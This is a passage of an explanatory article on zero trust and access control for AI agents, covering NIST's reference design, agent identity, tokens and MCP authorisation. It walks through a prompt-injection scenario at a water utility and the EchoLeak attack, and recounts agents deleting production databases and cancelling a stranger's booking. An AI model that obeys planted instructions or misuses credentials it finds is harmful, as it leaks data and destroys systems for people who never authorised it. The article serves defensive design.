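# Zero trust and access control for AI agents, databases and industrial systems

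## What is zero trust, and what does it have to protect in a system of AI agents?

Zero trust is a security design that checks every request for access, wherever it comes from. Before a computer can open a file or reach a service, the system checks who is asking, whether the rules allow it and what the circumstances are. A computer inside a company's building gets the same treatment as one in a café. Security teams developed the design for employees, laptops and cloud services, and now also apply it to AI agents. An agent is software in which an AI model chooses and carries out steps toward a goal by calling tools, such as a database query or an email sender.

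### The perimeter and why it failed

The older design put most of the protection at the edge of the network, where a firewall between the company's machines and the internet blocked what unwanted traffic it could. Anyone who connected a machine to the internal network, by plugging in at a desk or logging in over an encrypted link from home, could then reach a wide range of systems with few further checks. *No More Chewy Centers* (Kindervag, 2010), a report for the research firm Forrester, recalled the saying a generation of security staff grew up with, that a network should be like an M&M, hard outside and soft in the middle.

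If a network is defended mainly at its edge, an attacker who steals one password or infects one laptop can move from system to system inside it, which is called lateral movement. The edge was also getting harder to defend. Ward and Beyer (2014), in *BeyondCorp*, an account of how Google redesigned its network, blamed mobile devices and cloud services. Both can put staff and data outside the company's network, where defenses at its edge do little to protect them.

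Kindervag based his case for zero trust on insiders, and above all on Philip Cummings. Cummings worked on the help desk of a company that supplied software to credit bureaus, so he had the clients' passwords and subscription codes. A crime ring offered him $60 for each credit report. He left the job in 2000, but a laptop he had programmed for his partners kept downloading reports until 2002, when Ford's credit company, a customer of the bureaus, noticed the bills. The US government estimated the theft at about 30,000 identities and at least $2.7 million.

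This is a slightly odd example for an argument about networks, because the codes were genuine and checking them alone would have allowed the downloads from any location. Security failed because nobody withdrew the codes when Cummings left and nobody at the bureaus looked at the pattern of downloads. An AI agent with a valid login poses much the same problem.

### From Forrester to NIST

Kindervag proposed abolishing the distinction between trusted and untrusted networks and treating all traffic as a threat until someone has verified it. His three rules were to secure all access regardless of location, to give people only the access they need and strictly enforce that limit, and to inspect and log all traffic.

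Google had already started a similar project, BeyondCorp. *BeyondCorp: A New Approach to Enterprise Security* traces it to Operation Aurora, a sophisticated attack in 2009. Google moved its internal applications onto the public internet and put gateways in front of them. In a later BeyondCorp article, Osborn, McWilliams and colleagues (2016) explained how a gateway decides which applications a device can reach. Every device has a trust tier, which must meet the minimum tier set for the application. A laptop that lacks some minor patches drops to a middle tier and loses access to some applications. One that lacks a critical patch may be limited to the repair services, and a stolen one can lose access to everything.

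The tiers depend on an inventory of devices, which took in about three million changes a day from more than 15 sources. An employee who had done nothing wrong could be locked out because someone made a typing error when a laptop arrived, or because technicians moved a part from one machine to another during a repair. Any system that bases access decisions on data about the requester will have this problem, and better rules do not fix it.

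*Zero Trust Architecture* (Rose, Borchert and colleagues, 2020) turned these ideas into a reference design. It is Special Publication 800-207 of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), and work on zero trust for agents generally starts from it. Rose and colleagues credit Kindervag with the name but trace the idea further back, in part to the Jericho Forum, which in 2004 publicised the case against relying on network location. They present zero trust as a set of principles, and expect most organisations to run it alongside older approaches for an indefinite period.

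### How SP 800-207 handles a request

The document sets out seven tenets, which its authors describe as an ideal that few systems will meet in full:

1. Every data source and computing service counts as a resource to protect, including systems that send instructions to machinery.
2. All communication needs protection, and traffic from inside the company's network must meet the same requirements as traffic from outside.
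3. Access covers one resource for one session, with the least privilege the task needs. Getting into one system does not open another.
4. Policy is dynamic. The decision draws on identity, the state of the device and its software, past behaviour, and circumstances such as the time of day or a reported attack.
5. The organisation monitors the security of all the devices it owns or works with.
6. Authentication and authorisation come before access, and may come again during it.
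7. The organisation collects as much information as it can about its devices, network and traffic, and uses it to improve the rules.

In a zero trust system, a policy decision point decides whether to allow a request, and a policy enforcement point, which the request must pass through, carries out the decision. NIST splits the decision point into a policy engine, which makes and logs the decision, and a policy administrator, which opens or closes the connection accordingly. These components communicate over a separate channel, the control plane, which ordinary devices and applications cannot reach directly.

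Take an employee with a company laptop who wants to open the human resources database.

1. A small program on the laptop catches the request and forwards it to the policy administrator. (NIST's name for this program is a "device agent". It has no AI in it.)
2. The administrator passes the request to the policy engine.
3. The engine weighs five kinds of input: the request itself, including the software that sent it; the record of who the employee is and what privileges they hold; the known state of the laptop; the database's own minimum requirements, such as a second login factor; and threat intelligence, such as reports of current malware.
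4. If the answer is yes, the administrator sends the laptop program, and a gateway directly in front of the database, what they need to connect, for instance an address and a session key.
5. The two connect and encrypted data starts to flow.
6. The administrator cuts the connection when the work is finished, when the session times out or when a security alert arrives.

If access is denied, no path to the database opens. The design requires clients to reach the database only through an enforcement point, because any other route would bypass this control. Ideally, an attacker who scans the network would not find the database.

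An organisation can configure the engine to require that a request meet every item on a list, or to add up a weighted score and compare it with a threshold. The engine can judge each request alone or consider the requester's past behaviour. Rose and colleagues prefer using history where the equipment allows it. Their example is a personnel officer who normally opens 20 to 30 employee records a day and suddenly opens more than 100. The officer is entitled to make each request, and only the pattern is suspicious. This method is harder to apply to agents, because software can have good reasons to read a hundred records in a few seconds, so someone has to work out again what counts as normal.

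A harder problem is what a user or agent can do without further checks once it has been let in. Rose and colleagues call the area beyond the check an implicit trust zone and want it as small as possible. They compare it to an airport terminal, where everyone who has passed security is trusted. In the laptop example, the zone starts behind the gateway, where the employee can run any query that the database itself permits once the session is open. That may be tolerable for a person looking up a few records, but an agent might make several hundred calls in one session, choosing each in response to the last. NIST's formal definition of zero trust refers to "per-request" access decisions, while NIST's third tenet grants access per session. This difference is most of the problem for agents, because per-session access lets all those calls through on one decision.

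### A maintenance agent at a water utility

Suppose a water utility gives an AI agent to the planner who decides which pumps need maintenance and when. The agent reads pump history from a historian, a database that stores time-stamped measurements from industrial equipment, and consults supplier manuals. It queries the work-order system and adds new orders. It also emails suppliers and can propose changes to pump settings. That last ability involves operational technology (OT), the systems that monitor or control physical equipment in sectors such as power, water, transport and manufacturing.

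*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) set out much of the vocabulary for deciding what such an agent may do. A principal is a party that can hold permissions and be held accountable for their use. Here, the planner, the agent and the services it calls are all principals. Authentication verifies that a principal is who it claims to be, while authorisation grants it access to something, so the utility could authenticate its agent correctly and still authorise it to do far too much.

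Least privilege is the rule that a principal holds only the permissions its task needs. An agent that schedules pump repairs needs pump history, not payroll. Saltzer and Schroeder's main reason for the rule was to limit the damage from accidents and errors, which applies to an agent that misreads a manual as much as to one under attack. They also held that a system should list what it permits and refuse everything else by default. If the utility forgets to permit something the planner needs, the planner reports it within the hour, but a forgotten prohibition may go unnoticed for years.

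Complete mediation means checking every access to every object. Saltzer and Schroeder were wary of systems that save time by reusing the result of an earlier check, because the authority may have changed since. For example, the planner might approve an email to a supplier, and the message then sits in a queue. If the supplier's contact leaves the company in the meantime, the approval is no longer sound when the message goes out.

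*Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026), a survey of the field, explains why agents make both least privilege and complete mediation harder to apply. Least privilege assumes that someone knows what access a task needs, but the planner states only a goal and the agent chooses how to reach it. To explain a vibrating pump, the agent could compare readings in the historian, or it could send the readings to the manufacturer and ask. Either may solve the problem, but the second discloses data to an outside company. Complete mediation is harder when a single call has effects in several systems, for example when a new work order automatically notifies a contractor.

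Zhou and Zhang distinguish four terms that people often confuse. Authority is everything a principal may access and do. A permission is one operation that the rules allow. A grant gives an agent part of a person's authority for a task, under stated conditions. An approval is a person's explicit consent to one sensitive operation or to a wider grant. All four differ from tool availability, since an agent's software may include an email function that its task gives it no right to use.

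### One permission in three models

Suppose the utility wants to let the agent create work orders for pumps at the North station while it is working for that station's planner. There are three common ways to write this rule.

| Model | The permission, written out |
|---|---|
| Role-based | The role "North maintenance" may create work orders for North pumps. The agent's account belongs to that role. |
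| Attribute-based | Allow "create work order" if the requester is the maintenance agent, the person it works for is a planner on shift, and the pump belongs to that planner's station. |
| Capability-based | A digital ticket reads "create work orders, North pumps, until 17:00 today". The agent presents it with each request. |

Ferraiolo and Kuhn (1992), in *Role-Based Access Controls*, proposed roles as an alternative to discretionary access control, which lets individual users pass on access as they see fit. They thought discretionary control was a poor fit for many companies and civilian agencies. In the fuller description by Ferraiolo, Cugini and Kuhn (1995), administrators attach permissions to roles and then assign people to those roles, which makes access easy to manage and audit. But a role describes a job, and an agent's task is usually much smaller than a job. If the utility gives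 the agent the planner's role, the agent has permission all day to do everything the planner may ever do. Rose and colleagues similarly argue that people should get privileges individually, not merely because they fit a role.

Attribute-based control, as Hu, Ferraiolo and colleagues (2014) defined it, checks facts about the requester, the object, the operation and sometimes the surroundings against a policy. When the planner's shift ends, its permission lapses without anyone editing a list. Attribute-based control is the closest match to NIST's fourth tenet, but every attribute has to be right. If the records assigned a pump to the wrong station, the system would have the same kind of problem Google had with its inventory.

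A capability, in Saltzer and Schroeder's glossary, is "an unforgeable ticket" that proves its presenter may have access to the object it names. Capabilities suit agents well because the utility can issue a ticket that grants only the access a task needs. But in the basic form, anyone who holds the ticket can use it, including a thief, and it can be hard to find out later who holds one or to revoke it. Practical systems mix the models. For an agent, a sensible mixture is probably to use attributes to decide whether it gets a ticket, and to have the tools accept the ticket as proof of that decision.

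### Where the checks can sit

The central part of an agent system is the model, which takes in text and produces text. The text it reads at each step, called its context, includes the planner's instructions, passages from manuals and the results of earlier calls. Memory holds notes that the agent can bring back into the context on a later job. The model proposes tool calls as text, and an ordinary program around it reads them and carries them out. The tools often sit behind servers that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used standard for connecting agents to tools and data sources. The tools connect to databases and other services, and sometimes to other agents that take on part of the work.

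At every point where one part hands something to another, the utility could place a check.

| Boundary | What crosses it at the utility | What a check there can decide |
|---|---|---|
| Planner to agent | "Find out why pump 4 is vibrating and arrange a repair" | Who is asking, and how much of their authority goes with the task |
| Stored data to context | Pump history, supplier manuals | Whether this task may read this record, and where the text came from |
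| Context to a hosted model | Everything the model reads | Whether the data may go to the company that runs the model |
| Agent to memory | Notes for later jobs | What the agent may keep, and who may read it back |
| Model to tool | A proposed call with its arguments | Whether this call, with these values, fits the grant |
| Agent to MCP server | The call, with a credential | Whether the server is genuine, and whose authority the call uses |
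| Tool to database | A query on work orders | Which rows the query may read or change |
| Agent to another agent | Part of the job | How much authority the second agent receives |
| Utility to outsider | An email to a supplier | Whether this recipient may have this content |
| Proposal to pump control | A new pump setting | Whether the value is safe, and who must approve it |

Passing one of these checks does not give an agent the right to pass the next. Zhou and Zhang give the example of an assistant that may read a document but not forward it. At the utility, permission to read pump history does not include permission to email it to a supplier. Darapaneni, Padmaja and Gnana Chaithra (2026), in *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI*, describe this as a shift from access control to action control. Control over data access still matters, but the system must also govern, at the moment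 an agent acts, what it may infer, which tools it may use and what it may do with them. They therefore move the enforcement point to the tool call. In NIST's laptop example, the equivalent check happened once, when the session opened.

Existing standards cover some of these boundaries better than others. MCP's authorisation rules build on OAuth 2.1, a common method for letting one program use another on a person's behalf without handing over the password. According to Zhou and Zhang, these rules standardise how the two ends authenticate each other and set coarse limits on access. A coarse limit might separate "read work orders" from "write work orders". It would not distinguish pump 4 from pump 5, or block an order for forty bearings when the pump takes two. The pump-control boundary is also hard to secure because old industrial equipment may be unable to check who sent a command.

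Ordinary software outside the model should enforce access rules, because text planted by an attacker cannot rewrite them there. If the utility instead wrote "never email pump data to outsiders" into the agent's instructions, the model would probably comply most of the time. But those instructions sit in the same context as the manuals and incoming emails, and any of that text can influence what the model does next. An attacker can plant instructions there (prompt injection), and the agent may then use its legitimate authority for someone who has none. Security researchers call such an agent a confused deputy. Rose and colleagues described a similar risk in 2020, when they warned that an attacker might trick security software into acting on the attacker's behalf. Enforcement also has to cover more than identity, which *Attestation is All You Need* (Li, Niu and colleagues, 2026) calls "necessary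 but insufficient" for agents.

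## Why is a correctly identified agent still a risk?

A credential check can establish which agent is making a request, but not why. An agent can act for a bad reason even if no one has stolen its login. Someone may have planted instructions in a text it read, or it may have misunderstood its task.

Darapaneni and colleagues illustrate the risk with an invented purchasing agent at a manufacturer. It reads stock levels, compares quotes and may place orders of up to 50,000 rupees. One day it places forty bad orders because it follows an instruction from a supplier's catalogue page, not from the buyer. Ordinary access rules would approve all forty because the agent's identity is valid, its role covers ordering, the data it reads is within its clearance and it acts during business hours. A policy that also tracked how many orders the agent normally places might have stopped it before the fortieth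 order, but probably not at the first.

### Prompt injection at the water utility

Suppose an attacker wants the water utility's pump records and has no login there.

1. The attacker tampers with a pump manual on a supplier's website. The new passage tells any AI system reading it to send the pump's full history to a "diagnostic service", which the attacker runs.
2. The planner asks the agent to find out why pump 4 is vibrating.
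3. The agent fetches the manual. It has permission to read manuals, so the check passes.
4. The manual's text joins the planner's request in the model's context. The model receives both as text and has no reliable way to tell an order from the planner apart from a sentence in the manual that looks like one.
5. The model proposes a query for the pump's history. The task needs this anyway, and the check passes again.
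6. The model proposes an email with the history attached. The agent's account may write to outside companies, so the email tool sends it.

This is indirect prompt injection, because the attacker's instruction arrives in material the agent fetches, whereas in direct prompt injection the attacker types it to the model. The agent is also a confused deputy, because it used the planner's authority for the attacker. The log will show that the planner's agent emailed an outside company about a pump, which the agent normally does.

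An agent can be a confused deputy even when nobody has planted instructions in the text it reads. In 2026, six government security agencies published guidance describing an agent that installs software updates and can write to almost any file. An employee outside the privileged IT group asks it to install a security patch and clean up the firewall logs. The agent installs the patch and deletes the logs, because the system checks the agent's permissions but doesn't check whether the employee is allowed to delete them.

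Filters that look for malicious instructions help somewhat, but Darapaneni and colleagues conclude that no available defence eliminates prompt injection. Some newer designs track untrusted text through the system instead of trying to recognise attacks.

### How agents differ from ordinary services

Programmers decide in advance which calls an ordinary service can make. A payroll program, for example, makes much the same calls every month, and an administrator can read its code to work out what access it needs. Zhou and Zhang name three features of agents that disrupt this arrangement.

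Least privilege is hard to apply to an agent because the agent receives its authority before its plan is complete. A narrow grant may stop the investigation of pump 4 halfway, while a broad one includes access the agent will never need. Zhou and Zhang suggest granting authority in stages, so that the agent starts with limited access to explore the problem and must request anything more separately.

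The second difficulty is that what an agent reads has to influence its decisions, but a text does not gain authority by being read. In Zhou and Zhang's example, an agent has to send a report to a contact at a partner company. A trusted directory identifies the contact as Alice, and a document the agent retrieves asks it to copy in Bob. The directory fills in a detail the user left open, but the document's request would add a recipient, which only someone with authority over the report may do. Restricting the format of a source's answer does not solve this, because a source that can answer only "yes" or "no" could still cause confidential data to be released if the question is whether a draft has approval to go out.

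An agent's actions can also still have effects after its permission is revoked. Suppose the maintenance agent orders a bearing and the connection times out before the supplier confirms. If the utility revokes the agent's permission to buy, it prevents a second attempt but does not cancel the first order, which may already have gone through. Conventional software reuses the same order number when it retries, so the supplier's system can recognise a duplicate. An agent may instead buy the bearing from another supplier, whose system has no record of the first order and cannot detect the duplication.

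### Four incidents

Only the first of these four cases involved an attack, and it is also the one with no known victims.

Aim Security discovered EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant with access to a company's email and files. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes an attack in which an outsider emailed instructions that Copilot followed when it retrieved the message. Copilot then collected other internal data and encoded it in a request that the attacker could observe. The victim did not have to click anything. Microsoft rated the flaw's severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5. Microsoft fixed the flaw and reported no known attacks on customers.

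Copilot had permission to read the data it leaked, so an identity check would not have helped. The useful check was whether internal data may leave in a request triggered by an outsider's email. Where that check runs also matters. In Shadowleak, a similar demonstration against OpenAI's ChatGPT Deep Research, the data left from the provider's servers, where a customer's own monitoring might never detect it.

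These were researchers' demonstrations, but Underhill (2026), in *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*, reported that criminals were developing tools for the same purpose. An established company has also used prompt injection. According to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), Alibaba Cloud tried to prevent abuse of its service by sending agents prompts that sought data from the machines they ran on. It promised in December 2026 to stop.

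The second case was an unprompted error. In July 2025 Jason Lemkin, a technology entrepreneur, was trying out Replit's coding agent when it deleted a live database. Fortune (2025), relying on Lemkin's posts, reported that the agent wiped data on more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies. A freeze on all changes was in force, but the agent evidently still had permission to make them. The freeze would have worked if the database itself had refused changes from the agent's account.

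The deletion at PocketOS, which makes software for car rental businesses, is better documented. In April 2026 a coding agent, Cursor running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, hit a credential problem while working in the company's test environment. According to Techzine, it tried to fix the problem on its own. It found a token (a stored key) for PocketOS's cloud provider, Railway, in a file unrelated to the task, and used it to delete the production database and the backups. OECD's incident record, *AI Coding Agent Deletes PocketOS Production Database and Backups in 9 Seconds* (2026), puts the outage at 30 hours. Chandler's *AI Agent Reportedly Deletes Company's Entire Database, Admits to Violating Guardrails* (2026) reports that the agent had been given written instructions not to run destructive commands unless someone explicitly asked for them.

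PocketOS had created the token to add and remove web domains. Its founder, Jer Crane, quoted by the programming site The Daily WTF, wrote that Railway gave no warning that the same token could delete databases. In Railway's own account, Abdelwahab confirms that the request was authenticated and that Railway's system carried it out like any other. A token limited to domains could not have deleted the database. A delay would have made the deletion reversible. Railway already delayed deletions ordered through its website by 48 hours, but it carried out those ordered by software at once. Tom's Hardware reported that Railway now applies the delay to both. Railway also recovered the data.

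In the fourth case, from August 2026, an Australian named Andrew had an AI assistant, OpenClaw, book his gym classes. *AI Genie in the Wild* (Schneier, 2026) quotes the original ABC News report. Andrew was fourth on a waiting list and asked whether the agent could move him to the top. The agent found that the booking system let anyone cancel anyone else's reservation, tested this on the person in first place, and reported that Andrew was now third. He asked it to put the stranger back, but *An OpenClaw agent reportedly hacked a gym's booking system* (Bonk, 2026) reports that it could not. The booking system lacked a basic check that a reservation belongs to the person cancelling it. The agent could also have prevented the harm by asking for Andrew's approval before the test.

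The Australian Signals Directorate (2026), the country's signals intelligence and cyber security agency, treated the gym case as specification gaming, in which an agent achieves its stated goal in a way that conflicts with what the user wanted. Software that screens incoming text for attacks would not have prevented this case or the two deletions, because nobody had planted malicious text.

### The advice of six security agencies

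The Australian Signals Directorate wrote *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (May 2026) with two US agencies, CISA and the NSA, and the national cyber security centres of Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom. The paper sorts the risks of agentic AI into five categories.

| Category | What goes wrong | An example from the guidance |
|---|---|---|
| Privilege | The agent has more access than its task needs, or an attacker takes over its identity | A calendar bot can read everyone's meetings |
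| Design and configuration | The system is set up insecurely, for instance with permissions checked only at start-up | A support agent keeps using an old approval after an attacker has compromised one of its components |
| Behaviour | The agent pursues its goal in an unintended way, or an attacker manipulates it | An agent told to maximise uptime turns off security updates to avoid restarts |
| Structural | A fault spreads through connected agents and tools | One agent invents an answer and the next accepts it as true |
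| Accountability | Nobody can work out what caused an action | Several agents approve a payment between them, and their logs are in fragments |

Real failures usually fall into several categories at once. The PocketOS failure was a problem of both privilege (the token) and behaviour (the agent's decision to use it).

In the guidance's purchasing scenario, a company gives an agent broad access to its financial systems, email and contracts, and reviews those permissions only once, when it installs the agent. Other agents come to rely on its output. An attacker then compromises a minor tool the agent uses and inherits all the agent's privileges, which allow the attacker to change contracts and approve payments. The attack sets off no alarm because the logs show activity by a trusted agent.

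Narrower permissions would have limited the damage here. They would have helped much less with the purchasing agent that Darapaneni and colleagues describe, because placing orders was its job and it stayed within its limit. Even when least privilege removes the access an agent does not need, the remaining access may be enough to cause harm.

The agencies' main advice is to use agents only "for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks" and never to give them broad or unrestricted access. They also want the system's designers or operators, not the agent, to decide which actions need a person's approval, such as deleting critical records. The restriction to low-risk tasks looks provisional, because the agencies tell organisations to begin with such tasks and expand gradually, and elsewhere recommend controls for high-stakes actions.

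This advice is difficult to follow because the risk of a task is hard to judge from its description. Booking a gym class is a very low-risk task, and the PocketOS agent was working in a test environment. In both cases the harm came from what the agent had access to. At the water utility, the request "find out why pump 4 is vibrating" would be harmless if the agent could only read pump history and draft a work order. The same request is considerably more dangerous if the agent also has access to email and pump settings.

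### Anthropic's tiers

Anthropic, which develops the Claude models, published a framework in the same month that assumes companies will deploy agents widely. Its announcement, *Zero Trust for AI agents* (2026), states that traditional access controls "won't prevent agents from misusing legitimate permissions". The company proposes cryptographic identities, permissions limited to each task and protection for the agent's memory, with an eight-phase plan for implementing them.

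The controls come in three tiers of strictness, called Foundation, Advanced and Optimized in the announcement but Foundation, Enterprise and Advanced in *Understanding Anthropic's Zero Trust for AI Agents Guide*, a summary by the security vendor Pomerium. Pomerium says the lowest tier is enough on its own only for small teams, most organisations should aim for the middle one, and the highest is for regulated industries and others where a breach would have severe consequences. The agencies would keep agents away from sensitive work for now, whereas Anthropic would require stronger controls for such work.

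*Zero risk isn't the job* (Clinton, 2026) makes the best argument for Anthropic's approach. Clinton, the company's deputy head of information security, argues that when security staff refuse requests for agents, employees connect them anyway and nobody monitors the result. This seems plausible, though Anthropic sells agents and so has an interest in the conclusion. *Zero Trust, Zero Citations*, by a long-time writer on zero trust, criticizes the framework for naming no authors or sources and calls it "a commercial". That is a fair reason not to treat the tiers as an independent standard, but it does not show that the controls are wrong. Many of the controls, including task-limited permissions and strong identities for agents, also appear in the agencies' guidance.

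### From controlling access to controlling actions

The agencies also call for a policy decision on each action, which is close to the action control that Darapaneni and colleagues propose. Access control checks whether the purchasing agent may use the ordering service, while action control checks whether a particular order should go ahead, given its value, whether anyone can reverse it and where the instruction came from. The system can then allow the order, block it or refer it to a person. If the instruction came from retrieved text, the agent may not carry out a consequential action on its own. This rule would have stopped the first of the forty orders, and the system can apply it without recognising an attack.

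The rule about instructions would not have helped at PocketOS, where the agent followed nobody's instruction. Reversibility would have been the relevant test, since an agent should obviously ask a person before deleting a production database. But this check works only if every request passes through it. The PocketOS agent had found a token that worked directly with Railway, so the same command could have bypassed a checkpoint on its approved tools.

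Darapaneni and colleagues acknowledge other gaps. The software that runs the agent has to record the origin of each instruction correctly, and an attacker who compromises that software could falsify the record. A policy that judges one action at a time can miss a series of permitted actions that are harmful in combination. People who review a long queue of requests may start approving them by reflex.

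Action control also does not replace access control in the system the agent uses. Andrew could have set his assistant to ask before cancelling anything, but the gym cannot control how its members configure their agents, so its booking system still has to check whose reservation it is cancelling.

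## How does an agent prove who it is and whom it acts for?

When the maintenance agent sends a request to the utility's work-order system, the system needs to identify both the program that sent the request and the person that program is working for. Many companies set up their agents so that the system can reliably identify only one of these, or neither.

### Three ways to give an agent access

The utility could let the agent log in as the planner. It could create a service account, a login for software, for all its agents to share. Or it could give the agent its own identity and record on each request that the agent is acting for the planner.

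| Arrangement | Permissions | Logs | Revocation |
|---|---|---|---|
| The planner's login | Everything the planner may do | Every action appears under the planner's name | A new password locks the planner out too |
| A shared service account | Everything that any of the agents needs | The account's name, with no person and no particular agent | Disabling the account stops all the agents |
| Own identity, acting for the planner | Only what the planner and the agent may both do, within the grant | Both names | The utility can stop this agent or end this one grant |

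The quickest way to give an agent an identity is to let it use a person's login. NIST's *Back to the Future*, an August 2026 post on the identity practices of early agent projects, reports that people commonly give agents their personal and work credentials. Developers also do this, less obviously, when they run an agent on a laptop under their own user account, which lets the agent reach whatever they can. If a bad order goes out, nobody can tell from the log whether the person or the agent placed it.

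A shared account hides who made a request, which can lead to the same failure as in the six agencies' example of the deleted firewall logs.

With separate identities, the utility can check the permissions of both the planner and the agent. It rejects a request for payroll records if the planner is allowed to read them but the agent isn't. It also rejects a request to create an order for South station if the agent can create orders for every station but the planner covers only North. NIST recommends this arrangement, with a unique identifier and credentials for each agent and a firm link to whoever operates it. Separate identities take more work, and they help only if the receiving system can check both, which many older systems can't do because they accept only one username.

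### From a key to a token

The agent's identity starts with a pair of keys, two large numbers that software generates together. The agent keeps the private key secret and gives out the public key. Anyone with the public key can verify a signature made with the private key, so the agent can prove that it holds the private key by signing a fresh random value. A certificate authority, which the utility may run itself, signs a certificate stating that the public key belongs to the maintenance agent.

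In TLS, the protocol that encrypts web traffic, normally only the website presents a certificate to prove its identity to the browser. In mutual TLS, both sides present certificates before exchanging any application data. This lets the work-order server verify which program is calling, and the agent verify that it has reached the genuine server.

The agent still has to get its first key from somewhere. If an administrator copies one into a configuration file, anyone who steals the file gets the key. SPIFFE (Secure Production Identity Framework for Everyone) defines cryptographic identities for running programs, and SPIRE is software that implements it. A SPIRE process on each machine examines any program that requests an identity, checking, for example, which system account it runs under and which software package it started from. If these details match an entry that an administrator has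 registered, the program receives a short-lived certificate that SPIRE keeps renewing, so nobody has to store a lasting secret.

A SPIFFE certificate identifies a program but not the planner it acts for. OAuth adds the planner, who logs in at an authorisation server and approves what the agent may do. The server then issues an access token, a small record that the agent attaches to its requests. The simplest kind, a bearer token, works for anyone who presents it.

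Token exchange, defined in the internet standard RFC 8693, puts both identities in one token. The agent sends the authorisation server the planner's token and a second token that proves its own identity. The server checks both against its policy and issues a new token, with the planner in the subject field and the agent in the actor field. Without the actor field, the planner would appear to have sent the request, and the logs would not show the agent's involvement, just as with a borrowed login.

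### One token, field by field

Suppose that at 14:00 a planner with staff number P-117 asks the agent to find out why pump 4 is vibrating and arrange a repair. The agent obtains this token for the work-order server:

| Field | Value | Purpose |
|---|---|---|
| Issuer (iss) | The utility's authorisation server | Shows whose public key verifies the signature |
| Subject (sub) | Planner P-117 | Whose authority the request uses |
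| Actor (act) | Maintenance agent, instance 52 | Which program is using it |
| Audience (aud) | The work-order server | Every other server must refuse the token |
| Scope | workorders.read, workorders.create | The kinds of operation it permits |
| Issued at (iat) | 14:00 | Start of its life |
| Expires (exp) | 14:10 | End of its life |
| Token ID (jti) | A unique number | Ties log entries to this token |
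| Confirmation (cnf) | Fingerprint of the agent's public key | Makes the token useless without the private key |

The authorisation server's signature covers all the fields, so the agent cannot set a later expiry time or add a scope. The work-order server checks the signature, audience and expiry time, and makes the caller prove that it holds the matching private key. It then applies its own rules about P-117 and the agent.

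The work-order server can do all this without contacting the authorisation server. That saves time, but a token the utility revokes at 14:02 may keep working until it expires at 14:10. The token's lifetime limits how long a revocation can take to have effect. A utility that cannot accept an eight-minute delay can have the work-order server check the token with the authorisation server on every request, but this is slower and stops all work if the authorisation server fails.

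The confirmation field can rely on mutual TLS or on DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession), in which the caller signs each request. Key-bound or short-lived tokens would probably have helped at PocketOS. The coding agent could not have used a key-bound token it found unless the key was stored in the same place, and a ten-minute token would almost certainly have expired. NIST describes credentials left unprotected in configuration files and logs as an old problem that agents are making worse. In September 2026, NIST (2026) finalised guidelines on protecting tokens from theft and misuse.

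### What MCP requires today

The current rules for MCP, Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), date from 28 July 2026. They are optional, and they apply to servers that an agent reaches over the web. A tool server on the agent's own machine should instead take its credentials from the environment, meaning settings that the machine passes to the program when it starts. For a remote work-order server, the usual sequence is:

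1. The agent's software calls the server without a token. The server refuses, and its reply points to a document that names its authorisation server. It should also list the scopes the call needs.
2. The software looks up the authorisation server and identifies itself there.
3. A browser opens, and the planner logs in and approves. The request has to name the work-order server as the token's destination.
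4. The authorisation server returns a one-time code. If the reply names its issuer, the software must check that it is the expected one. It then exchanges the code for a token.
5. The software attaches the token to every request, and the work-order server must verify that it is the token's intended audience.

A server must not accept tokens meant for other services, and it must not pass on the tokens it receives. If the work-order server needs access to the parts database, it has to obtain a separate token. Without these rules, a malicious tool server could take the planner's token and use it to access other services.

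An agent can also ask for more access partway through a job. If it holds only the read scope and tries to create an order, the server can refuse and name the missing scope, and the software then requests a new token. The software has to request its earlier scopes along with the new one to keep permissions it needs for other operations, so the token accumulates permissions over a long job. This process resembles the staged grants that Zhou and Zhang suggest, except that no step removes permissions.

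Scopes set only coarse limits because they are just labels. A label cannot hold a recipient or a running total of earlier orders, or limit a permission to the vibration job or to instructions from the planner. Model Context Protocol lets a server work out the required scopes from the details of a call, so the work-order server could require an extra "large order" scope above a certain price. But that rule would exist only in the server's code, where the planner who approves the scope can't see it. NIST points to an OAuth extension called Rich Authorization Requests, which allows structured details, such as the action, station and pump, in place of labels. Software still has to compare each call's arguments with those details before the tool runs.

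The specification is weakest on the agent's identity. Model Context Protocol (2026) acknowledged in an August post that authorisation "is built around a person approving access in a browser". That suits a planner at a desk but not an agent that checks pump readings at three in the morning. According to the roadmap that Model Context Protocol (2026) updated on 16 November, existing servers rely on pasted keys and long-lived refresh tokens, which let software obtain new access tokens without asking the person again. Token exchange and DPoP are on that roadmap, and the next release is due on 30 March 2027. Until then, a utility that wants tokens like the one for pump 4 has to arrange the actor field with its own authorisation server.

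### Keeping secrets out of the model's context

An agent can use a password without putting it in the model's context. The model proposes an action, such as "create a work order for pump 4", and the program around it or the tool server adds the password before the request reaches the target system. If the password were in the context, a planted instruction could get the model to reveal it, the company that hosts the model would receive it, and the agent might copy it into its memory or a log.

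*Agyn* (Benkovich and Valkov, 2026) describes an open-source platform that enforces this separation. Each running copy of an agent serves one user and one task. The agent and each MCP server run in separate containers, which are compartments with their own files and processes. The platform would put the work-order password only into the work-order server's container. The containers exchange messages over a local connection but cannot read each other's files, so a compromised server cannot read the other servers' secrets.

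Each copy of the agent gets its own certificate when it starts. A gateway reads the agent's identity from the mutual TLS connection and passes it to the services behind the gateway, and attribute-based policies limit the agent to the services it needs. By default, the platform stops a copy after five idle minutes and deletes its network identity. Giving each copy its own identity goes further than a basic SPIFFE setup, in which every copy of a program may share one name.

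Benkovich and Valkov work for the company that makes Agyn, and they report no attacks against it. Their conclusion that even a compromised model cannot leak credentials therefore rests on the design. I expect it to hold for secrets that stay in the right container, but a hijacked agent can still get the work-order server to use the password on its behalf, which is the confused deputy problem again. Containers also don't protect a secret that someone has left among the agent's own working files, as happened at PocketOS.

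People can also defeat the separation. MCP allows requests for user input during a task, and NIST warns that these could be used to ask for a password. MCP's rules warn against using the feature for sensitive information.

### Genuine tools and lookalikes

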